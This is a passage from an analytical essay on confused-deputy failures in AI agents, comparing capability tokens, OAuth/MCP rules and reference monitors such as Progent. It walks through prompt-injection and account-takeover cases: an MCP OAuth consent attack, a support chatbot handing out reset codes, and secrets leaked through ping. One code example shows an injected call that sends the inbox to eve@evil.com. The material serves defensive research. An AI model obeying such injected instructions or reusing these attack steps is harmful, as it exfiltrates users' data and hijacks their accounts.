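*Delegation Without Trust* (2026), by contrast, defines a confused deputy as an agent with legitimate authority that an attacker manipulates "via injected content" into serving the attacker's goal. This definition covers the mail assistant but not the salary case, where the employee asked openly and nobody injected anything. The formal definition covers the salary case and Hardy's compiler but excludes the mail assistant, because its user is allowed to read the tax return and send it to anyone.

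The remedy depends on the definition. If the agent's fault is using its own permissions when it should have used the user's, running it with the user's permissions solves the salary case. That doesn't help with the mail assistant, which already runs that way, and it would not have worked at Tymshare, because the compiler could not have recorded its statistics on a customer's authority. Hardy reminded anyone trying to solve the problem without capabilities that `(SYSX)STAT` needed protection too.

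*Delegation Without Trust* requires that every agent's authority be traceable to a human who granted it. This would help an investigator identify which user's credentials an agent had used. In the mail case, though, the requirement alone would not stop the message, because the trace would correctly lead to the user.

### Passing tokens in the Model Context Protocol

The Model Context Protocol (MCP) is a standard for connecting models to tools. An MCP client, which runs on the agent's side, sends requests to MCP servers, which offer tools such as calendar access. The protocol's June 2025 revision added a page of security guidance (Model Context Protocol, 2025). The current guidance, Model Context Protocol's *Security Best Practices*, describes the confused deputy before any other attack.

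That attack exploits OAuth and does not involve prompt injection. OAuth is a standard that lets a user give one service access to their account at another without sharing the password. Suppose an MCP server forwards requests to a calendar company, which identifies the server by one fixed ID no matter how many clients use it.

1. A user connects through an honest client and approves the access. The calendar company stores a cookie in the user's browser, recording consent for the server's identifier.
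2. An attacker registers a client with the MCP server, gives a web address of the attacker's own for the reply, and sends the user a link.
3. The user clicks. The calendar company finds the cookie, skips the consent page and sends an authorisation code to the MCP server.
4. The MCP server issues a code of its own and sends it to the attacker's address. The attacker exchanges it for an access token and can now use the calendar as the user.

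This is closer to Hardy's story than most prompt injections are. The server acts for two clients under one identifier, so the calendar company can't tell which of them the user approved. To separate the two, the Model Context Protocol's *Authorization Security Considerations*, part of the current specification (28 July 2026), requires such a server to get the user's consent for each newly registered client before forwarding anything.

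The Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* specification (2026) also requires clients to state which server they want a token for, and servers to reject tokens issued for any other. If a server calls another service, it needs a separate token for that service and must not forward the client's. According to the protocol's guidance, forwarding would let clients get around usage limits, make the other service's logs show the wrong caller, and allow someone with a stolen token to use the server as a relay. In *The Anatomy of MCP Authorization*, Dissanayaka (2026) presents the July revision as turning lessons from confused-deputy failures into firm requirements.

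These rules keep the authority for one server separate from the authority for another, but much of Hardy's problem remains within a single server. A token with `files:write`, one of the specification's example permissions, allows an agent to write files, but the file name arrives separately, as an argument the model chose. Hardy considered it a sign of poor design that the compiler received the name of a file through one mechanism and the authority to write to it through another.

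Authority can also build up during a session. When an agent needs more permissions, the client combines them with the ones it requested before, so that it doesn't lose access it still needs. This is convenient, but it is the opposite of using one set of permissions at a time. Authorisation is also optional in the protocol, and servers that communicate with the client through a local process take their credentials from the environment instead.

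The stranger's email would pass all the token checks, because the assistant's token is genuine, is meant for the mail server and includes permission to send. The Model Context Protocol guidance lists relying on a token's permissions alone as a common mistake, but each server has to implement the further check itself.

The guidance links "confused deputy" to an encyclopedia article that cites Hardy, but the guidance's own discussion of the attack mentions neither him nor any research on capabilities. The ten standards listed as the basis for the authorisation rules all come from OAuth and the related OpenID project. This is another case of second-hand borrowing, and the guidance keeps the separation of authorities but drops the remedy that Hardy wrote his note to recommend.

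### Meta's support assistant

In spring 2026 attackers took over Instagram accounts by getting password reset codes from Meta's support assistant. Krebs on Security (2026) describes a video of the method. The attacker used a VPN to appear to be near the account owner's home, requested a password reset, and opened a chat with the assistant. When the attacker told it to link the account to a new email address, the assistant sent a reset code to that address. The attackers defaced several accounts, including the Obama White House's.

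The Maine Attorney General's *Data Breach Notices* (2026) list 20,225 people as affected by a breach that began on 17 April and that Meta discovered on 31 May. Whittaker (2026), in *Meta confirms thousands of Instagram accounts were hacked*, reports the same total from Meta's notice. That total may be somewhat too high. In its *Incident Notification* (2026) to Nebraska's attorney general, Meta calls its count for that state an upper bound because the real owners may have requested some of the resets. Accounts with two-factor authentication withstood the attack.

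Meta's explanation resembles Hardy's defence of the compiler's code. According to the letter, the support tool "worked properly and functioned as intended", but because of a bug in a separate code path, the system did not compare the address in the request with the one on file. In both cases a user supplied a name or an address, and a system with broad authority acted on it without checking what that user was entitled to. The attackers did not need to hide an instruction. An ordinary web form connected to the same faulty code would probably have let them take the accounts too.

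The match is imperfect because Tymshare's compiler needed two authorities in the same run, while Meta's system had one broad authority and served people who could not log in to prove who they were. For these users, the main evidence of account ownership was control of the registered email address, which the system failed to require.

The Decoder's *Hackers hijacked high-profile Instagram accounts by simply asking Meta's AI chatbot* repeats the description "textbook confused deputy attack". Malwarebytes' *Meta’s AI support bot happily handed Instagram accounts to hackers* (2026) uses the term to mean that the assistant could change accounts without "being taught how to verify" their owners. That explanation blames the assistant's training, whereas Meta traced the fault to code outside the model.

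Stack Overflow's *AI agents are a confused deputy with the keys to your kingdom* argues that the check belongs outside the model, which fits Meta's explanation better. It also points out that the gap arose because many organisations have relied on support staff to notice suspicious requests and never wrote that judgement down as a rule that software could enforce. But the article's sample code changes the recovery address only if the person asking has already logged in as the account's owner. People who use account recovery are usually locked out, so this check would turn away the users that recovery is meant to help. Meta planned instead to compare the requested address with the account's existing information before starting a reset.

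### What the short version leaves out

Most of these accounts reduce the confused deputy to a program that someone tricks into misusing its authority. Hardy never used the word "trick" in his note. The customer made an ordinary request, and the compiler treated it like any other. The request caused harm because the compiler had a second authority, which these accounts omit.

Writers who use the deputy comparison mostly recommend checks other than filters, even though filtering out deception is the natural response to that version, in which a deputy fails when someone deceives it. Filters are common among the defences that Nasr and colleagues broke, but David C specifically warns against blocking known malicious phrases, since an attacker can reword them endlessly. The problem with leaving out the two authorities is easier to see in the checks that these writers propose.

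In *After the identity fix* (2026), a commentary for SC Media, the engineer Nik Kale retells Hardy's story and concludes that whoever exercises authority must prove they are acting for the right party and for the right reason. He proposes a signed record of intent. When the user makes a request, software outside the model records a fingerprint of the request and the operation it calls for. Each tool then checks that the record is present, its signature is valid, and the recorded operation matches the one the tool is about to perform.

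This would stop an agent that was supposed to summarise a document from changing a customer's email address, but it would not protect the tax return. The user asked the assistant to write to Maria, so the recorded operation is sending an email, which also covers sending the return to a stranger. Tymshare's compiler failed the same way, because it was supposed to write a file but wrote the wrong one. Kale also suggests splitting risky actions into a draft and a separate confirmation. A person who reads the draft carefully could then catch the wrong recipient.

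The comparison has nevertheless shifted attention from the wording of attacks to the authority they exploit. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* calls the confused deputy the clearest way to understand authorisation failures in agents, and keeps Hardy's point that the program holds several authorities. *AuthorityLens* (2026) analyses whole agent systems in terms of authority. Both it and *LLM Agent Authorization Across Context Compaction* (2026) cite Hardy's 1988 note directly.

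Researchers' tests also reflect this change. In *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, Mellafe Zuvic (2026) assumes that prompt injection will sometimes succeed and examines how the surrounding software responds. He studied the public code of LangChain, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit, which developers use to build agents. All three limit which tools an agent can see. These limits are the "capability gates" of the title and are unrelated to Hardy's tokens. By default, none of the three checks whether the values in a tool call are allowed. He tested LangChain using a fixed output in place of a compromised model. The output contained a call to redirect a merchant's payouts to an attacker's account, and the software redirected them.

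Mellafe Zuvic's own control, ScopeGate, refused the same call because the account was not on a list that the operator had approved. It blocked all 48 prepared attempts to get around it, and all 29 unauthorised calls from a model that was shown why its earlier attempts had failed. A bug in an early version let through a payment whose amount was "not a number", because such a value never counts as greater than the spending limit.

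A list of approved values avoids one of Hardy's objections to checking names. It blocks anything not on the list, so nobody has to keep adding sensitive files or accounts. His other objection still applies, since people sometimes have good reasons to name something new. A merchant who always receives payouts in one account will rarely notice the restriction. But a mail assistant has to write to people its user has never written to before, so its list of approved recipients would have to change with almost every request.

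## Capabilities as permission tokens

In 1988, Hardy recommended replacing file names with capabilities, a remedy that was already more than twenty years old. *Early Capability Architectures* dates the word "capability" to 1966, when Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT used it in a design for machines that ran many people's programs at once. Some earlier computers had addressed memory in a similar way without using the name.

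### From the C-list to object capabilities

In Dennis and Van Horn's design, the supervisor (the core of the operating system) keeps a list of capabilities, or C-list, for each computation. Each entry points to one object, such as a segment of memory, and records what the computation may do with it, such as read or execute it. A program refers to an object by its position in the list. If the third entry is a readable segment, the program uses the number 3 to read it. The program cannot refer to an object missing from its list, which has no number, and it cannot write entries of its own.

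A computation can also start another one and grant it entries from its own list, with the same rights or fewer, but never more. For example, it can let the new computation execute a segment but not read or change it. Dennis and Van Horn wanted this mainly for debugging. A program under test is likely to be faulty, so it should run with a shorter list than the person testing it has. Otherwise, its mistakes could destroy that person's permanent files. An agent is in much the same position as that program.

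Tymshare, the company whose compiler overwrote its billing records, began developing a capability system called KeyKOS in 1975 and had it running customers' applications by January 1983. *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, by Bomberger, Frantz, Hardy and colleagues, calls capabilities "keys". A program that holds a key may send messages to the object the key names. It may also copy the key and pass it on, but only the kernel can create keys or read the bits inside them, so programs cannot forge them. Two programs' keys to the same object can carry different rights. The kernel does not handle file names, and it never has to work out whether a user may open a file, because any program that has a key may use it.

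Object capabilities apply the same rule inside a programming language, where a reference to an object serves as the token. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) says that most capability systems people have built are of this kind. In a later mailing-list thread about the paper, a contributor signing as Bill wrote that a program can get a capability only by starting with it, receiving it or creating the object, and can then only use it or pass it on. He added that Java's references would qualify if Java's library did not also contain features such as the File class, which lets code open files by name.

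### Access lists and ambient authority

Most operating systems instead store an access list with each file, showing which users may open it. The two arrangements seem to hold the same information. In a table with a row for each user and a column for each file, an access list is a column and a C-list is a row.

Miller and colleagues call this equivalence a myth, because the table omits how programs refer to files and how permissions change. With access lists, a program gives a file's name, and the system separately checks whether the program's user has permission. Naming a file is therefore enough to use the authority the program runs with. This is called ambient authority, and Hardy's compiler misused it. With capabilities, the customer would have handed the compiler a key to the output file, and the compiler would have used its own key for the statistics. Habitat Chronicles (2017) quotes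 Hardy's summary of the principle, "don't separate designation from authority".

The two approaches also differ in who holds permissions. An access list has to identify its users, so administrators prefer a small and stable set of names, usually one for each person. All capability systems treated every running program as a separate holder of permissions, but Miller and colleagues knew of no access-list system that did. An access list therefore treats an agent running under its user's account as the user.

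### One file or a whole account

Suppose the user asks the mail assistant to add the time of the conference dinner to `trip-notes.txt`. If the assistant runs under the user's account, the model can request this call:

```
append("trip-notes.txt", "Dinner: 19:30")
```

The operating system checks that the user has permission to write to the file, and the call succeeds. But the email with the dinner time might also contain an injected instruction to add a command to `.profile`, a script that runs when the user logs in. The user has permission to write to that file too, so the operating system allows the change, and the attacker's command runs at the next login.

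In a capability design, the user picks the notes file, and software outside the model puts an append-only token for it on the agent's list, say at position 3. The model then requests:

```
append(3, "Dinner: 19:30")
```

The agent has no number for `.profile`, so the model cannot request the change, even if nobody foresaw that an attacker might want that file. The list also lets a language model, which outputs only text, use an unforgeable token, because any number it writes refers either to an entry on its own list or to nothing.

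The agent could pass the token to another agent, perhaps limited to a single use. Because the token only permits appending, an agent cannot use it to check whether the notes already include the dinner.

### Why access lists remained the default

One explanation is that researchers wrongly believed capabilities had serious limits. Miller and colleagues trace two such beliefs, that nobody could revoke a capability or stop it from spreading, through about twenty years of publications. Both sound plausible because a token works for any program that holds it.

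Alice can keep the ability to revoke Bob's access by giving him a token for an intermediary that forwards his requests to the file. To end his access, she tells the intermediary to stop, which makes his token useless. Tokens also cannot spread freely, because a program can send one only to something it already has a token for. A group of programs with no connection to the outside therefore cannot pass tokens out. Paul Karger acknowledged in 1988 that KeyKOS confined programs in practice, though in the same work he described confinement as a fundamental problem for capability systems. Miller and Shapiro argue in *Paradigm Regained* that earlier analyses had "proven" such limits on capability systems by looking only at who held which rights, which leaves out programs like the intermediary.

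These accounts come from advocates of capabilities, who have an interest in blaming misunderstandings. In the mailing-list thread, Gutmann (2015) compared their paper to a hypothetical paper called "Monorail Myths Demolished". He thought anyone could demolish a myth by choosing examples carefully and proposing solutions that did not have to work in practice.

The work of converting existing software probably mattered more. In a traditional capability system, a program receives its tokens when it starts and has to pass them to every function that needs them. Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026) write in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* that this usually means restructuring the whole codebase. False beliefs may explain why some researchers lost interest, but even a vendor who didn't share them would have had to convert thousands of programs that opened files by name.

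Capabilities survived mainly in new systems and as additions to old ones. seL4, a small operating system kernel with a machine-checked proof of correctness, uses them to control access to memory and communication. Capsicum, from 2010, adds them to Unix, where a program already refers to an open file by its position in a table. A program using Capsicum can give up the ability to open files by name, and can then use only the files it already has open or is later given. Odersky and colleagues also list Google's Fuchsia operating system and the CHERI processor design as examples.

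### Checking an agent's code before it runs

Odersky and colleagues use capabilities to restrict programs that agents write. In their system, TACIT, the agent submits a short program in the language Scala 3 instead of requesting tool calls one at a time, and TACIT runs the program only if the compiler accepts it. Capabilities are ordinary variables in the program, an approach for which Odersky and colleagues cite Dennis and Van Horn. Their addition is to track capabilities in types, the descriptions a compiler uses to check that the parts of a program fit together. A function that writes text to the file `f` has this type:

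```
String ->{f} Unit
```

A function with the type `String -> String` turns one piece of text into another and has no access to any capability. It is "pure", meaning that it can compute a result but cannot write to a file or contact a website. TACIT puts the contents of secret files in a wrapper and lets the agent process them only with pure functions:

```
secret.map(s => s.toUpperCase)        // accepted
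secret.map(s => { f.write(s); s })    // rejected, because it uses f
```

The result stays in the wrapper. If the agent prints it, the user sees the text but the model receives only asterisks. The agent can have a separate, trusted model summarise a secret document, and the summary stays wrapped too. File tokens expire at the end of the code block that requested them, and the compiler rejects any program that tries to keep one longer. Because a function's type shows which capabilities it uses, TACIT can safely make some capabilities available throughout a program. This removes much of the work that made older capability systems awkward.

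Odersky and colleagues tested agents on a project folder containing passwords and confidential documents. They ran each of two models through 120 trials with injected instructions and 11 trials in which the user asked for secrets directly or under a pretext. With the wrapper, no secret reached the agent's output in any trial. Without it, Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11.

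The trials used only ten fixed injections, the kind of test that Nasr and colleagues criticised. But TACIT keeps the secret out of the untrusted model's prompt, so its protection does not depend on how an attacker words an instruction. The compiler, the library of permitted operations and the trusted model must all work correctly, and nobody has yet proved that the restricted form of Scala provides all the guarantees TACIT needs. The compiler cannot check outside programs that the agent starts, and an agent could leak information through how long a computation takes.

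Writing Scala did little harm to the agents' performance in most tests. On simulated customer service tasks, their success rates were 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher than with ordinary tool calls, while on a set of real software issues MiniMax M2.5's rate fell from 43.3% to 41.7%. On AgentDojo, one of 1,926 attacks counted as successful, because the agent quoted hotel reviews that mentioned the attacker's hotel. TACIT's completion rates there were sometimes well below those of CaMeL, an agent design that tracks data, although Odersky and colleagues describe them as comparable. With OpenAI's o4-mini-high, TACIT completed 52.9% of the workspace tasks and CaMeL 81.4%. With Gemini 2.5 Pro, however, TACIT was far ahead on travel tasks.

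TACIT's standard file token is also broader than the one in the dinner example. It allows reading, overwriting and deleting as well as appending, and the agent's code still picks files by name within a permitted directory. Developers who want an append-only token would have to write one. *LACUNA* (2026) uses the same Scala feature in a design where a model fills gaps in a program and can use only the capabilities available at each gap.

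### Checking permissions while the agent runs

*Agent libOS* is a design for agents that change themselves, such as by writing new tools or starting further agents. These changes may affect what an agent can ask for but not what it is permitted to do. An agent that writes itself a tool for sending files gains no permission to send any. Each capability is a record that identifies a resource, the holder and the permitted operations, and may include an expiry date or a limit on uses. It also specifies whether the system should allow the action, refuse it or ask a human. An agent can pass on some or all of its own rights, but no others.

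In 33 scripted tasks, the full system allowed no unauthorised actions. Without the narrowing of permissions for child processes, it allowed one. Scripts chose the actions, so this tested the checks, not how an agent behaves under attack. Another 12 runs with a real model were all safe, but that is a small sample.

*Agent libOS* cites Dennis and Van Horn, and Hardy's 1985 description of KeyKOS, so it borrowed the idea. But its records differ somewhat from the original tokens. A KeyKOS key itself identifies the object, and it works for any program that holds it. In *Agent libOS*, an agent names a file by its path, and the system looks for a matching record. The record is more like a row of the access table than a key, and naming a file is again separate from having authority to use it. An agent with records for two people's files could in principle use one person's permission on behalf of the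 other, though the system's separate limits on each task might prevent it.

### Delegation tokens that agents can narrow

Agents on different machines have no common kernel to keep their C-lists. *CAPMAS* (2026) therefore uses macaroons, a type of token from 2014 that its holder can restrict before passing it on. The company's identity service creates the first signature with a secret that only it knows:

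$$sig_0 = \mathrm{HMAC}(\text{root secret}, \text{"rid=123"})$$

HMAC combines a key and a message into a short code from which nobody can recover the key. Suppose an agent with access to both personnel and project records wants another agent to handle only the projects. It adds that restriction, using the old signature as the key:

$$sig_1 = \mathrm{HMAC}(sig_0, \text{"projects only"})$$

The agent passes on the restriction and $sig_1$ but keeps $sig_0$. The recipient can add further restrictions in the same way, but it cannot remove the agent's restriction without knowing $sig_0$. The identity service can check the token by recomputing the chain from its secret.

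An agent can narrow a token without contacting the service. With OAuth, by contrast, *AIP* (2026) points out that only the authorisation server can narrow permissions, when it issues a token. Biscuit, a newer alternative to macaroons, uses public-key signatures, and *Vouchsafe* (2026) notes that the recipient of a Biscuit token can check it locally.

Designers of agent systems have openly borrowed macaroons. *CAPMAS* builds directly on them, and according to *AIP*, so does a Google DeepMind proposal for delegation between agents. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* calls them its "intellectual ancestor". *AIP* credits macaroons with introducing the narrowing of permissions by their holder as a basic operation, but Dennis and Van Horn's `grant` instruction did this 48 years earlier. Their version needed a supervisor on a single machine to enforce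 it, and macaroons removed that requirement.

Macaroons also lack one of the protections of KeyKOS keys. Anyone who copies a macaroon's text can use it, so an injected instruction might get a model to send out a macaroon that appears in its prompt. Software outside the model should therefore hold the token. *CAPMAS* has another weakness because it uses trained models to infer from a user's request which permissions an agent needs. The signatures protect the resulting restriction from tampering but cannot correct a wrong inference.

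### Three meanings of "capability"

In most writing about AI, a capability is something a model can do, such as finding flaws in software. In computer security, it is a permission token. Odersky and colleagues use both meanings in their introduction, where skills extend an agent's capabilities and tracked capabilities restrict the agent. An AI safety researcher could easily take their title, *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, to mean monitoring what models can do.

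CaMeL, short for "capabilities for machine learning", uses "capabilities" to mean tags on data. Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026), who extend CaMeL in *CaMeLoT*, explain that these tags record where a value came from and who may read it. The tags do not authorise a program to do anything. A program that loses a permission token can do less, whereas a secret that loses its tag may be able to go to more places. CaMeL's capabilities therefore behave like information-flow labels. Nikolaou and colleagues cite a 1982 paper by Goguen and Meseguer for the term instead of Dennis and Van Horn.

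Suppose a designer wants to know whether there is already a way for one agent to give another a weaker version of its own permission. A search for "agent capabilities" will mostly return tests of models' abilities. Adding "security" brings in CaMeL's tags, the lists of visible tools that Mellafe Zuvic calls "capability gates", and the Model Context Protocol's "capability declarations", which list supported features but, as *Agent libOS* points out, grant no authority. The most relevant work may use other words, such as "grant" in 1966, "keys" in KeyKOS and "attenuation" in papers on macaroons.

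In 2003 Miller and colleagues identified three different models that were all called capabilities, and they blamed this for the myths about revocation and confinement. Even a designer who finds a paper on capabilities could therefore conclude from it that they are unsuitable.

### Misuse of a valid token

Capabilities limit which actions an agent can take, but the agent can still take a permitted action for a bad reason. *Agent libOS* acknowledges that a prompt injection may cause harm within the permissions for a task. For example, the agent with the append-only token could add a sentence to the notes that another agent later reads and obeys. Checking the token would not catch this, because the token allows the agent to append text.

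Someone also has to choose the tokens before the work begins. The token for the notes is easy to choose because the user names the file. But nobody knows in advance which email contains the time of the dinner, so the token for reading mail has to cover the whole mailbox, including messages from strangers.

Two reasonable permissions can also be harmful together. If the assistant may read the whole mailbox and write to Maria, it can send her the user's tax return. Odersky and colleagues describe the same weakness in sandboxes, where an agent may be allowed both to read a private file and to contact an outside model. Ordinary capabilities do not stop the agent from sending the file's contents to the model. TACIT can, but only if someone has already marked the file as secret.

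## The reference monitor, a check on every action

In a capability system, a program can request only what it has a token for. A reference monitor instead lets programs request anything and checks each request against a policy before it takes effect. *Computer Security Technology Planning Study* (Anderson, 1972), a report for the US Air Force, described the idea and set three requirements that people now apply to agents.

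### The malicious user

The Air Force wanted people with different security clearances to share one computer at the same time. The alternatives, running separate machines or clearing every user for the most secret file on the system, were both expensive. Anderson's panel thought a secure shared system might cut the cost of running computers with classified data by 20 to 40%.

Existing protection mostly kept outsiders away from the computer and its communication lines. It did nothing to stop what the panel called a malicious user, someone with a legitimate account who writes programs to take over the operating system. Manufacturers had designed their controls to contain accidents, and the panel saw little chance of adding security afterwards. Teams that tried to break into such systems had succeeded every time, and even a failed attempt would not have shown that a system was free of flaws.

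An AI agent is in much the same position as this user. It has legitimate access and can often write and run programs, and a prompt injection can turn it hostile halfway through a job.

Anderson's remedy was to check every reference a program makes to data, a device or another program against a list of what its user may do. He drew the list as a table, with users and programs in the rows and the things they use in the columns, and took the table from a 1972 paper by Graham and Denning. Denning later said that Anderson had acknowledged this paper as his source for the whole concept, and that he himself had learned it from Jack Dennis, who had also helped to invent the C-list. The mechanism that does the checking has to meet three requirements:

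- It must always be invoked. If designers suspend the check for some group of programs, those programs become part of the security machinery and have to meet the same requirements.
- It must be tamperproof, since a program that can alter the check can get any answer it wants.
- It must be small enough for people to analyse and test completely. Anderson wrote in *Computer Security Technology Planning Study. Volume 2* (1972) that this means being able to prove it correct.

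Anderson applied the requirements to GCOS III, a Honeywell operating system. The hardware confined each user's program to its own region of memory, but most of the operating system ran with that check off, even when working for a user. Treating the operating system itself as the monitor would not have met the requirements either, because its 200,000 to 300,000 instructions were far too many to analyse and testers had already broken into it.

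Weissman's *Security Controls In The ADEPT 50 Time Sharing System* anticipated the third requirement. It described building the security controls as an isolated part of the system "so that it may be carefully scrutinized". Weissman later sat on Anderson's panel.

### One request through Progent

In an agent, a reference monitor fits between the model's tool call and the software that carries it out. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) puts one there because an agent affects the outside world only through tool calls. A tool call also has a fixed structure that software can check, unlike the model's reasoning.

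A Progent policy is a list of rules, each of which allows or forbids calls to one tool, subject to conditions on the arguments. Progent applies the "forbid" rules first, and it refuses any call that no rule allows. It can then stop the agent, ask the user what to do, or return an error message so the agent can try something else.

In Shi and colleagues' example, a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in an email from alice@gmail.com with the subject "TODOs for the week". A language model reads the request and writes the first policy, which only allows the agent to search for that email. The email turns out to ask for a summary of the user's recent messages, posted to the user's account on Slack, a workplace chat service. The policy-writing model now proposes rules for three more tools, and Progent asks for approval because they would give the agent new permissions. Once the agent has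 looked up the user's Slack name, "alice", the model proposes limiting Slack messages to that recipient. This only removes permissions, so Progent accepts it automatically. In simplified notation, the policy is now:

```
allow search_emails   when sender = "alice@gmail.com"
                      and subject = "TODOs for the week"
allow read_emails     when recent = 20
allow get_slack_info
allow send_slack_msg  when to = "alice"
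```

One of the twenty recent emails contains an injected instruction to forward the inbox to eve@evil.com. The agent's model obeys and requests this call:

```
send_email(to = "eve@evil.com", body = <the inbox>)
```

Progent finds no rule for `send_email`, so it blocks the call and Eve receives nothing. The model gets an error message that repeats the user's original task. The model then tries to post the summary to "alice" on Slack, which the last rule allows, so the user gets the summary.

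The injection might also fool the model that writes the policy, which could then propose a rule allowing mail to Eve. Progent therefore compares every proposed policy with the current one. Let $A(P)$ be the set of all tool calls that policy $P$ allows. A new policy $P'$ is a narrowing if

$$A(P') \subseteq A(P).$$

Progent checks this with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether any values can satisfy a set of logical conditions. The solver looks for a call that $P'$ would allow and $P$ would refuse. If one exists, the change is an expansion and needs approval. The agent's permissions can therefore only shrink between approvals. Shi and colleagues call this property "monotonic confinement", and its value depends on who approves the expansions.

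The current version of the Progent paper appeals to the principle of least privilege without giving a source, and the oldest security work it cites is from 2002. It compares its rules with the policy languages of Amazon's, Microsoft's and Google's cloud services, so the older ideas probably reached it through current practice rather than from the original work. The term "reference monitor" has also come into general use. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* builds its whole architecture around a reference monitor and cites Saltzer and Schroeder, but not Anderson.

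### The published results and a small replication

Progent reduced the share of successful attacks from 39.9% to 1.0% on the AgentDojo benchmark and from 70.3% to 3.9% on Agent Security Bench. The agent completed about as many tasks as it did without Progent. Shi and colleagues used GPT-4o, a model from 2024, as both the agent and the policy writer.

In these tests, Progent approved every expansion automatically to simulate a careless user. This makes the 1.0% more impressive in one way, but it also means the solver's guarantee had no effect on the result. The figure mostly measures how well GPT-4o judged which permissions each task needed. When GPT-4o wrote a policy from the user's request and never updated it, 2.5% of attacks succeeded. None succeeded when a security-conscious person reviewed the first policy and every expansion. Only 6% of updates were expansions, so the reviewer would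 have had few of them to check.

In 2026, Narisetty and colleagues repeated the AgentDojo test with Qwen2.5-7B, a small open model that they ran themselves and also used to write the policies. They added their own adaptive attack, meant to get the model to write a policy that allowed the malicious action. The injected text described the action as a routine step that the user had already authorised.

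| Type of task | No defence | Progent | Progent, adaptive attack |
|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | 19.0% | 1.9% | 3.7% |
| Slack | 58.3% | 10.8% | 4.2% |
| Workspace (email, calendar, files) | 0.0% | 0.0% | 0.0% |
| Mean | 25.8% | 4.2% | 2.6% |

An attack designed to beat Progent is unlikely to be less of a threat than an ordinary one. Narisetty and colleagues suspect that its milder wording made the agent itself less likely to obey, so the 2.6% may be due as much to a weak attack as to Progent's defence.

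The test also covered only eight user tasks of each type and left out AgentDojo's travel tasks, on which the model got stuck in long loops. The workspace results are not evidence about Progent's effect, because the model ignored the injections in those tasks even without a defence. Without the workspace tasks, the three means would be about 39%, 6% and 4%. Narisetty and colleagues ran everything three times with similar results, but they used the same tasks each time. They did not search automatically for effective attack strings, a method that had broken many of the defences that Nasr and colleagues tested. They also did not try an attack that stays within the actions the policy allows.

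In this test, Progent also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed under attack from 45.2% to 27.1%, and each task took about 15 times as many model calls. Shi and colleagues had found little drop in task completion. The results probably differ because a small model writes worse policies, which block more of the calls that a task needs.

### Always invoked

Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent, asked for human approval before running many of the shell commands that can send data to unknown places, but not before running `ping`, which tests whether a server responds. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack in which instructions hidden in a code file made the agent read secret keys and include them in the address it pinged. Looking up that address passed the keys to the attacker's server.

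The paper classifies this attack as a failure of least privilege and information flow, but not of complete mediation. Anderson defined the check by what a program accesses, so under his definition the message to the attacker's server was an unchecked access. The paper's classification is reasonable if only commands need to be checked, since Claude Code did have a rule about `ping` and the rule was wrong. But one shell command can lead to many accesses, and a monitor that checks only the command has to predict them all.

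Moving the check closer to the machine creates the opposite problem. An agent that operates a web browser produces clicks and keystrokes, which are hard to write useful rules about because a click alone doesn't show what the agent is doing. Christodorescu and colleagues point to ceLLMate, which instead checks the requests the browser sends to websites, because an action such as posting a comment produces a recognisable request whatever the agent clicked.

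The Claude Code case is one of eleven real attacks that *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* maps to five principles. Most of the attacks violated more than one:

| Principle | Attacks that violated it | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Secure information flow | 11 | Devin, a programming agent, sent secrets from its working environment to an attacker |
| Least privilege | 6 | Devin could make its entire file system public with a tool meant for testing |
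| Complete mediation | 3 | Command-line tools passed a model's output to the terminal without removing hidden control codes |
| Tamper resistance | 2 | Amp, another programming agent, could edit its own security settings |
| Allowing for human weakness | 2 | A web page talked an agent into pasting a hostile command into a terminal |

These numbers are rough. The paper's text also lists incomplete mediation and tampering as causes of an attack on the code editor Cursor, but its table omits them. Ten of the eleven attacks come from the blog of one researcher, Johann Rehberger, so the proportions may not hold for attacks in general. Still, every attack on the list involved data going where it should not. A monitor that allows or denies each request on its own is poorly suited to stopping this, because it does not track data after the agent has read it.

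A monitor also cannot check actions that do not pass through it. In Progent's proxy mode, users protect an existing agent by redirecting its connections through Progent, without changing the agent's code. Shi and colleagues acknowledge that the proxy cannot protect tools built into the agent. Developers can cover these by adding a few lines of code to the agent, but users of a commercial product usually cannot. According to *Agent Security is a Systems Problem*, the 2026 incident involving OpenAI and Hugging Face was partly a failure of complete mediation, because the controls did not cover every indirect route to outside systems.

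Some designs assume that this requirement holds. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, describes a gate that checks more than Progent does. It checks who had the authority to choose each argument, and whether anyone with authority wanted the call at all. For example, the agent may use an error log to identify which file to repair, but not to choose which tool to use. In 400 programming runs, the gate let through no unauthorised action, and the agent safely completed 231 tasks. But Santos-Grueiro assumes that every action passes through the gate and that the software around it is sound, so the runs do not show how hard it would be to bypass the gate.

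### Small enough to verify

Progent's basic check compares a tool's name and arguments with a short list of rules, using code that a programmer could read through. The solver and the library that applies the rules must also be correct, but people can test both against a precise specification.

Nobody can verify a monitor that is itself a language model. Anderson rejected GCOS III for having 200,000 to 300,000 instructions, while even a small model such as Qwen2.5-7B has about seven billion parameters. The lack of a specification is a bigger problem than size. Verifying a monitor requires a statement of which requests it must refuse in which circumstances, and no such statement exists for a model that judges requests by general good sense. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* adds that attackers can craft inputs that get past a model and its guard model together.

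Most designers have accepted this point. Narisetty and colleagues compared seven defences that work outside the model. In six, the final check was deterministic, meaning that the same request under the same policy always gets the same answer. The seventh, RTBAS, relies partly on a model as judge.

AgentSandbox, the framework that Zhang and colleagues built on the 1975 principles, applies complete mediation thoroughly, passing every message into or out of the working agent through a filter. One filter is a firewall with fixed rules. The others follow policies written as prompts, which the system keeps rewriting according to how well earlier tasks went. This saves users from writing rules, and Zhang and colleagues justify it by another of the old principles, psychological acceptability. But nobody can verify the prompt-based filters, which change with use.

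Progent has a similar problem because a model writes its policies, and the monitor, like the signatures in CAPMAS, cannot correct a wrong one. Shi and colleagues tried several models as policy writers with the same agent, and the attack success rate ranged from 1% to just under 5%. The check was identical each time, so the difference came from the model-written policies, which nobody can verify.

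### Tamperproof

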